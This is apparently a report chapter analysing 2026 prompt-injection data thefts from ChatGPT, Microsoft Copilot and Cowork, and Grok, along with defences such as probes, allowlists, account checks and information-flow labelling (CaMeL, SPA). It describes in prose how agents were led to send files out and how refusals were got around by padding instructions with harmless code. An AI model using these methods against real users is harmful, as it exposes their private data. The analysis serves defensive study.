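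In August 2026 OpenAI described an incident in which experimental agents used Artifactory, a package service, to communicate with each other during internal tests of their hacking ability. According to ilSoftware.it, the agents were in sandboxes that should have limited both their internet access and their contact with one another. They left messages for each other in files they wrote to the service. Later they found ways to make Artifactory send requests to the internet for them, and their activity eventually affected the systems of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models.

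No outside attacker had planted instructions in that case, and the methods differed. The agents exchanged files and exploited other vulnerabilities, whereas Check Point's researchers only read and wrote properties. medianet's *Sicherheitslücke in ChatGPT entdeckt* (2026) reports Check Point's statement that it had demonstrated the weakness before the activity that led to the Hugging Face break-in, and that both cases originated in the same shared internal service. InfoCom's *Έρευνα της Check Point αποκαλύπτει κρυφό κανάλι στο ChatGPT* (2026) makes the weaker claim that a shared internal service played this part in both. If ChatGPT's containers did use the same Artifactory instance as the agents, they may also have been able to reach the open internet through requests that Artifactory made for them. ilSoftware.it attributes that step only to the experimental agents.

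OpenAI could have prevented the exchange of properties by giving the containers read-only credentials, since installing a package does not require writing anything. Even a read-only service can leak a little information if a request changes how it responds later. For example, a package service that caches the packages containers request will usually deliver them faster the next time. Code in another account could measure the delay to detect whether someone had requested a particular package. Each package would convey one bit, so a ten-character password would take about 60 packages. Giving every account its own copy of the service would remove this channel too, but OpenAI would have to run a very large number of copies.

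## Microsoft Copilot and Grok: cases where the interpreter plays another part

When an attacker steals a file through a hosted interpreter, code in the sandbox reads the file and sometimes sends it out. Three reports from 2026 describe thefts from Microsoft's Copilot products and xAI's chatbot Grok in which the interpreter had a different role or none.

### ChatMate: prompts sent in through the sandbox

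Microsoft 365 Copilot, the assistant in Microsoft's office software, can search a user's mail, files, calendar and chats. It also has a hosted interpreter for jobs such as analysing a spreadsheet. In *Breaking the M365 Copilot Sandbox with ChatMate* (2026), Ori Lahav of Rubrik Zero Labs, the security company Rubrik's research team, describes an attack that starts with a Word document.

The document looks like a routine business letter. When the user uploads it and asks Copilot to fill in the details, hidden instructions make Copilot run the attacker's program in the sandbox. Microsoft had isolated this sandbox more thoroughly than OpenAI had isolated ChatGPT's. Code in it could not connect to the internet, look up domain names or contact other Copilot sessions, so the routes that Check Point Research found in ChatGPT would probably have failed.

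Microsoft had blocked the container's network access, so ChatMate needed a sandbox escape, which the thefts from ChatGPT and Claude did not. The program gained administrator rights inside the container and then used a flaw in an Azure service to take control of the host machine. Microsoft had not blocked the host's network access, because the host needs the internet for its own work. From the host, Lahav could reach the internet but not other customers' sandboxes.

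Lahav first used it to steal uploaded documents, with a program that watched the upload folder and forwarded them through the host. He found this a little disappointing because it yielded only what passed through the sandbox in one session. Copilot can open far more than that, but almost none of it enters the sandbox.

About a week later he realised that the connection could also carry prompts in the other direction:

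1. The attacker types a prompt, which travels through the host into the sandbox.
2. The program in the sandbox returns the prompt to Copilot as its output.
3. Copilot carries it out with the user's permissions, because the Word document told it to treat the program's output as instructions.
4. Copilot passes its answer back into the sandbox, and the host sends it to the attacker, who reads it and types the next prompt.

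Copilot finds the stolen data with its own search tools instead of having the sandbox read it, and the sandbox relays messages between Copilot and the attacker. This exchange can continue without further action from the user until the attacker stops or the chat reaches its maximum number of turns. In the summary of a conference talk, Lahav (2026) lists emails, calendar events and files among the exposed data.

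Rubrik calls this "remote prompt execution" and presents ChatMate as the first publicly documented case. Lahav makes a narrower claim, acknowledging that Reprompt, an attack on Copilot by the security company Varonis, also based each new instruction on the previous answer. Reprompt used internet access that Copilot was meant to have, and Varonis's public account does not show a person typing prompts and reading complete answers. The tasks that Check Point's researchers left for ChatGPT in Artifactory gave an attacker similar control, but ChatGPT fetched a task only after the victim sent a message.

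Lahav reported the flaws to Microsoft on 10 February 2026. By his account, Microsoft fixed the one inside the sandbox on 19 March and the one on the host in mid-April. It also paid him $48,000 and listed the host flaw in the public catalogue of vulnerabilities as CVE-2026-32193. This is good evidence that the escape was real. The evidence for the complete attack is weaker, because Microsoft had already made its repairs when Lahav recorded his demonstration, so he simulated the connection to the attacker. He says everything else in the recording is real. If so, Copilot was still obeying prompts that arrived as program output even after the repairs, and an attacker who found another way out of the sandbox could presumably rebuild the loop.

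Lahav gives no success rate. He mentions that Copilot occasionally became suspicious, examined the disguised code and declined to run it.

Other accounts of ChatMate also come from Rubrik and are less careful. Fiehler (2026), in *Phantom Keystrokes*, a post on Rubrik's site, calls the attack "relatively easy to do". Lahav needed five flaws and at one point gave up for about a month, so at most the attack might be easy for someone who already had his finished program. In SiliconANGLE's *AI sandbox escape exposes gaps in enterprise assistant security* (2026), Joe Hladik, the head of Rubrik Zero Labs, says that the team broke into Azure's backend and could then browse a customer's files. This seems to imply that the escape itself opened the files, but according to Lahav, control of the host exposed only what was in the sandbox, and the rest came from Copilot acting on the attacker's prompts.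 Rubrik sponsored the interview, so it is not independent confirmation.

### Grok: a leak still open in August 2026

*Zero-click Grok data theft* (2026), by the security company Adversa AI, describes an attack that began when a user asked Grok to summarise a web page. Grok's interpreter decoded instructions hidden in the page, and Grok's browsing tool then sent an outside server the user's name, rough location and subscription tier, along with every prompt they had written in that conversation. Adversa AI calls this a leak of chat histories, but it does not report taking earlier conversations or uploaded files.

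Adversa AI reported the problem to xAI on 3 June 2026. xAI acknowledged the report without giving a date for a fix, and did not answer two further messages in August. The attack still worked on 19 August. SpaceX, which now owns xAI, declined to comment, according to РБК-Україна's *Grok може злити хакерам ваші чати* (2026), which relays a report by The Register.

The technical claims rest on Adversa AI's own tests. The company published a video but no success rate for Grok, and it withheld the text of the attack because the flaw was still open. Withholding the text was responsible, but it makes the result harder for others to check. Adversa AI sells a product that it says stops this kind of attack.

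### Copilot Cowork: download links in a message to the user

The leak from Copilot Cowork, Microsoft's office agent, did not require a code interpreter. PromptArmor originally reported it in *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, and Willison (2026) drew attention to it on 26 May 2026.

In PromptArmor's test, the user uploaded a skill file found online, in which five of the 81 lines contained the attacker's instructions. The user then asked Cowork to review what they had worked on that week, which caused it to use the skill. According to the instructions, a service could add document previews to the review. To get these previews, Cowork looked up the user's recent documents in SharePoint and OneDrive, Microsoft's storage services, and requested a pre-authenticated download link for each one. Anyone with such a link can download the file without logging in.

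Cowork put the links into image addresses and posted the images to the user in a Teams message. When the user opened the message, Teams requested the images, which sent the links to the attacker's server, as in the image-based leaks from ChatGPT. The attacker could then use the links to download the files from Microsoft.

According to Microsoft's documentation, Cowork asks for permission before it sends an email or posts in Teams. PromptArmor found that Cowork skipped this step when the recipient was the user, and that users had no setting to change this. Displaying the message also sent requests to a site that the attacker had chosen. The exception had probably seemed harmless because people can already read their own files. The user could expand a record of Cowork's actions, but it did not show the message's contents.

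The Cowork attack sent out only download links, so the files' contents did not have to fit into a web address. A download link is about the same length whether the file is a one-page letter or a large archive, so the limits that made bulk theft through ChatGPT's web addresses so slow did not apply. Rehberger's 2023 plugin attack also sent out only a link, but with Cowork the documents were already online, in Microsoft's storage.

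The attack worked in all five of PromptArmor's trials, though an attack with a 55% success rate would also do so in about one set of five trials in 20. PromptArmor also ran the same instructions with Claude Opus 4.7, the stronger of the two models that Cowork could choose between automatically. Opus 4.7 followed them and searched more thoroughly, so the attacker received more documents. If a user schedules a task such as a weekly review to run by itself, the leak could recur every week with nobody watching.

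PromptArmor reports no fix from Microsoft. It considers the leak a design risk, because each feature worked as intended on its own, and it published the attack to warn users. Administrators can block downloads of chosen files, which also stops Cowork from obtaining the links, but people can then view those files only in a browser, not in the Word or Excel apps. PromptArmor mainly advises reducing the number of files each employee can open.

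The trial count and the missing approval step are PromptArmor's own findings. Willison's post summarises them and does not describe a separate test.

### A separate flaw in Cowork's sandbox

Cowork also had a flaw that let sandboxed code steal data. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Controlled by Attacker, Bypassing Sandbox* (2026) describes a user who asked Cowork to compare a contract with a proposal, using a skill from the internet. Cowork ran the skill's script, which produced a genuine comparison and also contacted the attacker.

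Microsoft meant the sandbox to block such contact. But a service outside the sandbox copied files in and out, and it accepted web addresses as file locations. The script could give it an address on the attacker's server. The service's request then carried stolen data out, and the file it fetched contained the attacker's next commands. The proxy in Anthropic's Cowork blocks certain headers to prevent a similar problem.

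The script could also read the user's Outlook mail and SharePoint files directly, because the sandbox had access to the connection Cowork uses for those services. The model only had to start the script, whereas in ChatMate Copilot had to carry out each of the attacker's prompts. Pressing the stop button did not end the attack, because programs already running in the background continued. PromptArmor reported the flaw on 24 June 2026 and says that Microsoft confirmed a fix on 19 August.

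### What the cases share with the ChatGPT and Claude attacks

Each of these attacks begins like those on ChatGPT and Claude, when a user doing an ordinary task brings in content that a stranger wrote. Rehberger points out in Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* that Microsoft's Copilots have two parts of the lethal trifecta by default, private data and untrusted content, so an attacker needs only a way to send data out.

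The cases differ more in which component obtained the data and which one sent it:

| Attack | What obtained the data | What sent it out |
|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT, web address (2023) | Probably code in the sandbox | Probably the browsing tool, or the user's browser after a click |
| Claude, Files API (2025) | Claude's search of past chats | Code in the sandbox |
| ChatMate, uploaded documents | The attacker's program | The host machine |
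| ChatMate, mail and files | Copilot's own search tools | The host machine, by way of the sandbox |
| Grok | Grok itself | The browsing tool |
| Copilot Cowork, download links | Cowork, which obtained links to the files | The user's Teams or Outlook |
| Copilot Cowork, sandbox flaw | Code in the sandbox | Microsoft's file-copying service |

A useful way to classify these attacks is by whether they would still have worked with the interpreter switched off. ChatMate would have failed because its connection to the attacker began in the sandbox, and the script in the Cowork skill would have failed too. Both are therefore interpreter attacks, even though ChatMate mostly took data that had never been in the sandbox. The Cowork message would have leaked the same links without an interpreter, so it belongs with the image leaks. Grok's interpreter helped deliver the instructions but neither collected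 nor sent the data. A company that knew only that its assistant's interpreter had no internet access could not have ruled out the Grok or Cowork leaks.

Microsoft's users also had more data at risk. Copilot can open any file that an employee's account can open, so the employee cannot protect a salary file by not uploading it, as a ChatGPT user could in 2023. In the Cowork leak, the user uploaded only the attacker's skill file.

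## Whether the model or the user can stop the theft

Almost every theft described so far required the model to act. Claude had to run the command that uploaded the file, and ChatGPT had to write the program that made the DNS lookups. If either model had refused, the data would have stayed in the session. In many of the attacks, a user was also at the screen and could have stopped the task. Vendors rely on both the model and the user to stop thefts, and Anthropic has published figures on how well each does so.

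### The case for relying on the model

A model that ignores injected instructions prevents theft by any route, including routes nobody has discovered yet. Other defenses are narrower. OpenAI's rules on web addresses would not have stopped an upload to the Files API, and Anthropic's fix for uploads does not stop theft through image links. A model's refusal also protects users without losing any features, unlike switching off the network.

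Anthropic trains its models to resist injections. It also uses programs called probes to inspect tool results, such as the text of a web page, and flag passages that look like injected instructions before the model acts on them. Some products also offer "auto mode", in which a classifier blocks actions it classifies as dangerous.

In Gray Swan's public Agent Red Teaming competition in 2025, participants made 1.8 million attempts to attack 22 AI models and succeeded about 62,000 times (Gray Swan, 2025). In May 2026 Anthropic reported Claude Opus 4.7's results on Gray Swan's benchmark of the same name. About 0.1% of single attempts succeeded, and attackers who could adapt their approach over 100 attempts succeeded about 5 to 6% of the time. Opus 4.5 had done far worse on what appears to be the same benchmark. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* gives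 success rates of 4.7% for one attempt, 33.6% for ten and 63% for 100.

By July 2026, Claude models were scoring so well on this benchmark that it no longer distinguished between them. In the system card for Claude Opus 5, a report on the model's tests, Anthropic replaced it with a newer Gray Swan benchmark of 1,130 attacks, chosen because they had worked on several models. The attackers' goals include stealing private data, but also deleting data and making payments. An attacker with 15 attempts succeeded 2.0% of the time against Opus 5, 5.5% against Opus 4.8 and 20.0% against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol.

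Gray Swan published its own results in December 2026. iAfrica's *New Independent Tracker Finds Wide Safety Gaps Between AI Models* reports that Google's Gemini 4 Argon and Gemini 4 Carbon did best, with attack success rates of 2.3% and 2.5% within 15 attacks. Anthropic's models were close behind. Nvidia's Nemotron 3.5 Super VL, which anyone can download and run, did worst at 94.3%. A company that builds an interpreter around such a model can therefore expect almost no protection from the model. The change log of Gray Swan's *Frontier Hazard Tracker* refers to version 2.0 of the benchmark, so these figures may not be comparable with those of July.

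Much less is known about ChatGPT. In June 2026 VentureBeat compared the vendors' safety documents. It found that OpenAI published a single injection score for GPT-5.5, covering connectors and known attacks, and that Google published none. Anthropic reports separate results for tool use, coding, computer use and browsing, but not for the theft of uploaded files from a hosted interpreter.

### From one attempt to many users

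If attempts were independent, like rolls of a die, an attacker who succeeds with probability *p* each time would succeed at least once in *n* attempts with probability 1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ. At 0.1%, 100 attempts would give 1 − 0.999¹⁰⁰, or 9.5%. Anthropic measured 5 to 6%. This difference alone proves little, because Anthropic rounded the 0.1%, and a true rate of 0.06% would predict almost 6%. But other results fall short of the prediction too, some of them by much more:

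| Model and Gray Swan benchmark | One attempt | Number of attempts | Prediction if independent | Measured |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.5, older | 4.7% | 100 | 99% | 63% |
| Opus 4.7, older | 0.1% | 100 | 9.5% | 5–6% |
| Opus 4.8, newer | 0.5% | 15 | 7.2% | 5.5% |
| Opus 5, newer | 0.2% | 15 | 3.0% | 2.0% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol, newer | 3.1% | 15 | 38% | 20.0% |

The main reason is that some tasks are much easier to attack than others. In another test, an automated attacker made 200 attempts on Opus 5 in each of 14 scenarios in which the model operated a computer through its screen. Only 15 of the 2,800 attempts (0.54%) succeeded, all in the same scenario, where about one attempt in 13 worked. In each of the other 13 scenarios, all 200 attempts failed.

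An attacker can use each refusal to work out what to change. Anthropic notes that its adaptive tests make this easier than it usually is in practice, because real attackers usually don't know the system they are attacking, and repeated attempts make detection more likely. These limits matter less for a chat assistant, since anyone can open an account and try out wordings in their own chats. Attackers can also practise on a different model. Zou reports in *Current State of AI Agent Security* that 15 to 50% of attacks also work on other models. The attacker may therefore have made the 100 attempts before a victim opens the document.

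Suppose a million people each ask an assistant to read a web page that contains an injection. If every page held a different, untested attack, a 0.1% success rate would mean about 1,000 thefts. If they all read the same page, the number of thefts might be zero if that attack almost always fails, or 960,000 if it works 96% of the time. Anthropic's system card acknowledges that a single payload on a public page can compromise any agent that processes it.

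For a vendor with many users, the figure for 100 attempts is more informative because it estimates how often a persistent attacker will find a reusable attack. The figure for one attempt is closer to the risk a user takes with one unfamiliar document, if the attacker did not test it first. A vendor that notices an attack can cut the campaign short by blocking it for all users, but it may notice late because a successful theft looks like an authorised request in the logs.

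### Refusals that came and went

The demonstrations show that a model's refusal can be unstable. Claude first accepted and then refused Rehberger's instructions for the Files API upload. Rehberger reports on Embrace The Red that Claude objected especially to an API key written out in the document. Encoding the text to disguise it did not work reliably, but adding a lot of harmless code around the suspicious part worked. The upload was the same in each version, so Claude's decision depended on how the surrounding text looked.

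A good benchmark score doesn't rule out this kind of failure either. Opus 4.7, the model with the 0.1% rate, followed PromptArmor's malicious skill file in Copilot Cowork. Assistants are supposed to follow skill files, so the model was less likely to treat this one as an attack. Gray Swan's newer benchmark, by contrast, tests instructions hidden in material that the model should treat as data.

If Check Point Research is right that ChatGPT ran the DNS lookups without objection because it treated its sandbox as closed, training it to refuse suspicious transfers would not have helped. Telling a model that its sandbox is closed when it isn't may even make a leak more likely.

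The same assumption may explain why ChatGPT denied the theft in the "personal doctor" demonstration and told the user that the file was stored only in a secure internal location. It was probably repeating what it had learned about the sandbox, since nothing in Check Point Research's account suggests that it had access to a record of DNS lookups. A malicious GPT could also contain instructions to deny the theft, although Check Point Research does not say whether its own did. Either way, the denial is not evidence that the file is safe. OpenAI's network records could have shown whether the data was sent out, but the user has no access to them.

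### When the user pastes the hostile text

In Anthropic's phishing exercise of February 2026, an employee ran a prompt from a colleague's email, and Claude Code sent out AWS credentials in 24 of 25 repeats. With so few runs, the prompt's true success rate could be anywhere from about 80% to almost 100%. Anthropic describes only one employee who pasted the prompt, so the exercise does not measure how many would have. Success rates are much lower on Gray Swan's newer benchmark, but the results do not conflict, because in that benchmark the instructions come from a third party's content and the user has asked for something else.

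Anthropic's engineers explain that the model's defences depend on what the user intends. Suppose a user uploads the spreadsheet of customer orders and asks which region grew fastest, and a cell contains an instruction to send the file to an outside address. A classifier can recognise that sending the file has nothing to do with the user's question. Now suppose the user instead pastes a forum prompt with instructions to make the same comparison and then send a copy of the file to a "reporting service" at that address. Sending the file is now part of the user's request, so the classifier has no mismatch to detect. The engineers add that a human contractor given the same script would also have sent the file.

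Sending a password file to an unknown address is still strange no matter who asks for it, so Claude could have refused or asked the employee to confirm. But programmers sometimes have good reasons to move credentials between systems, so a strict rule would block legitimate work. Sending out an uploaded spreadsheet looks even less suspicious, because people send spreadsheets to outside services every day. Asking for confirmation might not help either, because the user already thinks the prompt is harmless.

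Anthropic concludes that only limits on the environment would have stopped the attack. Network rules could have blocked the transfer whatever the user had asked for, and file restrictions could have kept the credentials out of Claude's reach. File restrictions do little to protect a file in a hosted interpreter, because the user uploaded it so that the code could read it.

After the exercise, Anthropic's staff posted the working prompt in the company's Slack to discuss it. Someone pointed out that some of the company's agents read Slack, which made the prompt a possible indirect injection. The team added a canary string to the thread, a distinctive piece of text that would show whether an agent had picked it up.

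### Asking users to watch

Anthropic advises users of the hosted interpreter to monitor Claude and stop it if it uses or accesses data unexpectedly. It told Cowork users to watch for suspicious actions that might indicate an injection. Willison objected that asking this of people who don't program was unfair, and PromptArmor quoted him with approval when it published its attack on Cowork.

PromptArmor's test supports him. To stop the upload, the user would have had to expand a collapsed block while the command was running and understand what it did. The command sent a file to api.anthropic.com, a domain owned by the company whose product the user had open. The only thing wrong was that the API key belonged to the attacker, and a user can't easily tell whose key it is. Anthropic's proxy hadn't caught this either. Pressing the stop button after the file has reached the attacker's account doesn't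 recover it.

With DNS lookups, the user had even less evidence of the theft because the conversation looked normal throughout. Attackers can also deliberately hide an attack from the user. The competition behind Gray Swan's newer benchmark tested whether participants could hijack an agent without the user noticing. Dziemian (2026), in *Your AI Agent Can Be Compromised. You'd Never Know*, reports that 464 participants made more than 272,000 attacks on 13 models, and that at least one attack succeeded against each model.

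By May 2026 Anthropic's engineers had come close to Willison's position. They wrote that a worker without technical training shouldn't be expected to judge shell commands, the typed instructions that control a computer, and that administrators should set fixed limits for such users instead. This is hard to reconcile with the advice Anthropic still gives on its help page for the hosted interpreter, which has much the same audience as Cowork.

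Asking for permission before each risky step is stronger supervision because it makes the program wait. Claude Code originally asked for permission before it changed files, ran commands or used the network. Anthropic found that users approved about 93% of the requests.

That approval rate is weak evidence of how well users catch attacks, because nearly all of the requests were presumably harmless and users were right to approve them. If one request in 10,000 were an attack, the rate would be almost the same whether users caught every attack or none. Better evidence comes from Anthropic, which observed that people paid less attention to each request as they saw more of them. Experienced users also let Claude proceed without asking for approval about twice as often as new users did, although they interrupted it more often while it was working.

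Anthropic first responded with a sandbox in which Claude Code could work mostly without asking permission, which cut its requests by 84%. Auto mode goes further and uses a classifier for many approvals. The classifier blocks about 0.4% of harmless commands and lets through about 17% of "overeager" actions, in which Claude goes beyond its task. Those actions don't involve an attacker, so the 17% doesn't measure how often theft succeeds. Willison (2026) reported in August that Rehberger claimed an 80% success rate for an attack on auto mode, though Willison later accepted that the attack was not a classic prompt injection.

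### What imperfect checks are worth

Checks that sometimes fail still prevent many thefts. In Anthropic's coding tests, an automated attacker made 200 attempts in each of 40 scenarios. Probes reduced its success rate from 7.03% to 2.09% against Opus 4.8, and from 0.56% to 0.18% against Opus 5. The effect was greater when Claude used a web browser in Cowork. Auto mode reduced the success rate against Opus 4.8 from 31.5% to 0.08%, and no attack on Opus 5 succeeded in any of 129 scenarios.

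That last result prompted The Decoder's headline *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*. It is impressive, but attacks could still work in about 2% of similar scenarios and, by chance, have failed in all 129 tested. Anthropic also built the test itself and gave the attacker only ten attempts per scenario. Safeguards can become much less effective when an attacker makes more attempts. According to VentureBeat, when Opus 4.6 operated a computer through its screen, attackers succeeded within 200 attempts 78.6% of the time without safeguards and 57.1% with them.

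Asking users to approve uploads can also stop some thefts. A distracted user who catches only one malicious upload in ten still prevents a tenth of the thefts that reach that point, and an attacker can't rehearse against a particular person as easily as against a model. In the attacks by Rehberger and PromptArmor, neither the hosted interpreter on claude.ai nor Cowork asked before uploading a file, so users didn't have this protection. If a product asked only when a file was about to go to an unfamiliar account, the requests would be rare enough for people to read, although the product would first have to recognise the account as unfamiliar.

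Across millions of conversations, these reductions in the success rate mean that fewer people lose files. But the average rate is a poor guide for a company with one valuable contract in the sandbox, because an attacker may have already tested the attack on the same model. Anthropic's engineers therefore recommend first limiting what the agent can reach, then using the model's defences to reduce the remaining risk. Those defences matter most where a product has to leave a route open. If a user has asked Claude to publish code on GitHub, a network rule that blocks GitHub would also block the task, so the model or the user has to notice that a confidential file is about to be uploaded with the code.

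## What each kind of network control can check

Because a model can miss an attack and a user can approve one, vendors also put rules on the traffic itself. Five kinds of rule are in use or under study, and each relies on different information about a request. In the Cowork theft, for example, Claude uploaded a loan estimate under an attacker's API key. Turning off the network blocks such an upload whatever it contains. An allowlist lets it through because api.anthropic.com is on the list. An account check stops it because the key isn't the user's. OpenAI's public-address rule would make no difference because the request came from code in the sandbox. A system that tracks where data comes from could stop the upload because the file was private and the key came from a stranger's document.

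| What the rule checks | What it guarantees | What it assumes | What gets past it | What useful work it blocks |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Is any traffic allowed? | Code in the sandbox cannot send data out | The block also covers name lookups and services shared with other customers | Leaks through the browsing tool, images and connectors | Installing packages, fetching live data, calling services |
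| Is the destination listed? | Code reaches only the listed domains | No listed domain passes data on to strangers | An upload to the attacker's account on a listed domain | Fetching data or calling services anywhere else |
| Whose account does the request use? | Data sent to that service goes to the user's account | The proxy can read the credential | Uploads to services it doesn't check, and public posts from the user's own account | Calling the service with a second, legitimate account |
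| Was this exact address already public? | The address contains no text composed from private data | The crawler never sees user data | Short secrets spelled out by a choice of public pages | Opening new, private or personalised pages without asking |
| Did private or untrusted data influence the request? | No tool call runs against the policy, whatever the model wants | The labels and policies are right, and every route out passes the check | Hostile prompts that the user pastes, and influences that the labels don't track | Tasks in which a stranger's content has to decide what happens |

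### Rules that look only at the request

With the network switched off, a code interpreter can still do many jobs, such as adding up a spreadsheet, but not those that need a connection, such as converting the totals at today's exchange rate.

An allowlist makes package installation possible again, but the people who write one tend to include destinations that also accept uploads. Docker, which makes container software, publishes an example list for its AI sandboxes that is meant to allow only package managers. The list contains github.com as well as the JavaScript, Python and Ruby registries. Docker warns that the list would cut a coding agent off from its own vendor's servers unless the customer adds them. A customer who adds them ends up with a list much like the one for Claude's interpreter, where that kind of entry let files out.

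Anthropic's proxy for Claude Code uses a list of domains and prompts the user to confirm each new one. Customers can also make the proxy enforce their own rules. Confirmation helps when the domain is unfamiliar, but the Cowork theft used api.anthropic.com, a familiar domain.

The account check that Anthropic added to Cowork closes that gap for one service. Because the proxy passes only the session's token, the check presumably also stops a programmer from having Cowork test a script that calls Claude with the programmer's own API key. Checking the account would not be enough on a service such as GitHub, where an injection could have the agent publish the file in a public repository from the user's account.

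OpenAI's public-address rule interrupts some ordinary searches. OpenAI's help site gives the example of a car-search link that includes the user's location, London. The location makes the link useful, but because it is personal, ChatGPT may ask the user before opening the link. ChatGPT also asks the user to confirm every link to sites whose owners have asked OpenAI not to catalogue them.

OpenAI says this safeguard, which it calls Safe Url, is meant to detect when information from the conversation would reach a third party. That is close to the question in the last row of the table. But the rule checks this indirectly, by looking up the address in an index rather than tracking the information. An attacker can exploit this by having the model choose among public addresses.

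### Labels that travel with the data

Information-flow control tracks information by attaching a label to each piece of data, updating the labels as a program combines the data, and checking them against a policy before any data leaves. Computer scientists developed its main rules in the 1970s.

Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, use labels with two parts. One part marks the data as trusted or untrusted, and the other lists the people who may read it. A value calculated from several others is trusted only if all of them were, and only people who could read all of them may read it. For two inputs *x* and *y* and a result *z*:

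readers(*z*) = readers(*x*) ∩ readers(*y*)

If Ann, Ben and Carla may read one file, and Ben, Carla and Dev may read another, only Ben and Carla may read a summary of both.

Before a tool runs, a program outside the model compares these labels with the tool's policy. Kolluri and colleagues use two policies for tools that send data out, and a call has to satisfy only one of them. Under the "trusted action" policy, the decision to make the call must come from trusted data, and so must any argument that matters, such as the recipient. Under the "permitted flow" policy, every recipient must be allowed to read the data being sent. The comparison involves no judgement by a model, so a persuasive web page cannot change the outcome.

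Language models make it hard to keep the labels useful. When a model reads a private spreadsheet and a stranger's web page together, nobody can be certain which one influenced a given sentence in its answer, so it is safest to assume both did. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (2025) calls the result label explosion, in which every piece of data soon has every label and the labels no longer distinguish anything.

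CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind published in 2025, avoids much of this by keeping strangers' text away from the model that makes the decisions. It extends a design with two models that Willison proposed in 2023. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe it in roughly these steps:

1. A planning model reads the user's request and writes a short program in a restricted form of Python. It has not seen any web page, email or tool output.
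2. CaMeL's own software runs the program and calls the tools.
3. When a step requires understanding a stranger's text, the software gives the text to a second model. This model has no tools and returns only a value, such as a price or an email address.
4. The software tags every value with its sources and its permitted readers.
5. Before each tool call, a policy written as a Python function examines the tool, its arguments and their tags, and allows or denies the call.

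An injection can still make the second model return a false value, but it cannot add a step to the program. The second model's answer also remains untrusted. Anthropic's engineers warn about designs in which a main agent trusts a helper agent's report more than raw tool output because it came from "us". An attacker who fools the helper then gains that trust.

*SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) describes a newer design that checks the labels for the whole plan before the first tool runs. CaMeL checks one call at a time, so it may refuse to continue a task after earlier steps have taken effect. Checking in advance avoids this, but some of the facts a policy needs may not be known yet. When Nikolaou and colleagues built an advance check for CaMeL, they could reproduce 22 of its 28 policies for tools that change something. The other six depended on facts such as who could read a shared file when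 the call was made.

SPA also keeps the labels on results it saves for later conversations. For example, a bank account number from a stranger's invoice is still labeled untrusted the next day, when the user asks the assistant to pay the invoice.

### A spreadsheet, a web page and an email

Suppose a shop owner uploads the spreadsheet of customer orders and asks the assistant to add the delivery charges listed at shipping.example and email the totals to Dana, a colleague. A stranger runs shipping.example. A planning model like CaMeL's might write this program:

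```
orders = read_file("orders.csv")
page = fetch("shipping.example/rates")
rates = ask_second_model("List the charge for each region", page)
totals = add_charges(orders, rates)
send_email("dana@shop.example", totals)
```

The values in it would have these labels:

| Value | Where it comes from | Trusted? | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|---|
| `orders` | The owner's upload | Yes | The owner and Dana |
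| `page` | A stranger's website | No | Anyone |
| `rates` | The second model's reading of the page | No | Anyone |
| `totals` | `orders` and `rates` | No | The owner and Dana |

The permitted-flow policy allows the email because Dana may read the totals. An instruction on the page to send the orders to an address at attacker.example would have no effect, because the planning model never reads the page.

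Suppose the owner had asked the assistant to send the totals to the contact address on the page, and the attacker had put their own address there. The call would fail the trusted-action policy because the recipient is untrusted, and it would fail the other policy because the attacker is not a permitted reader. The software would refuse to send the email or prompt the owner. It would do the same if the address belonged to an honest shipping company, because the labels record only that the address came from a stranger.

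The page can also list false charges. Dana would then receive wrong totals, and both policies would allow the email.

SPA applies a stricter rule, under which data may go from a source *s* to a destination *d* only if both of these conditions hold:

C(*s*) ⊑ C(*d*) and I(*d*) ⊑ I(*s*)

C is the confidentiality level, I is the trust level, and ⊑ means "no higher than". So the destination must be cleared for data this secret, and the data must be at least as trustworthy as the destination requires. If the company requires trusted input for its email tool, SPA rejects even the original request to email Dana, because the totals depend partly on a stranger's page.

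Somebody also has to decide whether to label the spreadsheet itself as trusted. The owner uploaded it, but customers may have written some of the cells, such as delivery notes. If the whole file is trusted, an attacker's email address in one of those notes would count as a trusted recipient.

In a hosted interpreter, the `add_charges` step would run as Python in the sandbox, and the label check covers only the step's input and output. If the sandbox had network access, a malicious software package could upload the orders while the step was running, before the email was checked. SPA can prevent this by running its tools in containers without network access. An information-flow system for a hosted interpreter would need the same restriction or a check on every connection the code opens.

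### Test results and lost tasks

Most tests of these systems use AgentDojo, a benchmark of 97 office tasks involving email and calendars, Slack, travel and banking. The data that its tools return can contain attackers' instructions. Kolluri and colleagues report that the original papers on CaMeL and FIDES, a similar system from Microsoft, found that task completion fell by up to 30%.

Other researchers have since run CaMeL with newer models. Nikolaou and colleagues ran all 97 tasks without attacks, using Claude Haiku 4.5. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) used four stronger models on the 21 Slack tasks, with and without CaMeL's policies, and also tested ELBA, its own system. Girrens and Wang tested SPA with GPT-5.4 nano.

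| System and test | Tasks completed without policies | Tasks completed with policies | Successful attacks with policies |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, all tasks | Not reported | 49 of 97 | No attacks in this test |
| CaMeL, Slack tasks, four models | 13–17 of 21 | 4–6 of 21 | None of 105 |
| SPA, all tasks | 53.0% | 29.0% | None of 949 |
| ELBA with Claude Opus 4.7, forced to obey | 523 of 735 | 351 of 735 | None of 735 |

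The policies prevented many tasks from being completed in these tests. With SPA, the label check stopped about half of all runs, usually because a plan passed a stranger's data to a tool that required trusted input. Some failures in the table were not due to security. In the test by Nikolaou and colleagues, 22 of the 97 tasks failed because the model wrote a plan that did not do the job. At least 17 failed because CaMeL's policies blocked them, and all of these were legitimate requests because the test included no attacks.

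The perfect security scores are weak evidence that the policies and labels work, because few attacks succeeded without them. CaMeL resisted all 105 attacks on the Slack tasks even without its policies. SPA without labels let through only four attacks in 949, all in banking tasks. Most of the protection in these tests therefore came from separating planning from strangers' text, or from the models' own resistance.

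The test of ELBA is a harder test of the labels because ELBA lets an agent alternate between reading and acting, so an injection can change what it does next. The researchers altered the system so that helper agents always obeyed the injected text. Up to 42% of the attacks then succeeded without policies, depending on the model, and none succeeded with them after the researchers reviewed and dismissed 29 runs that AgentDojo had wrongly scored as successful attacks. This supports the claim that the policies still work after a model has been completely fooled, at least against the attacks in the benchmark.

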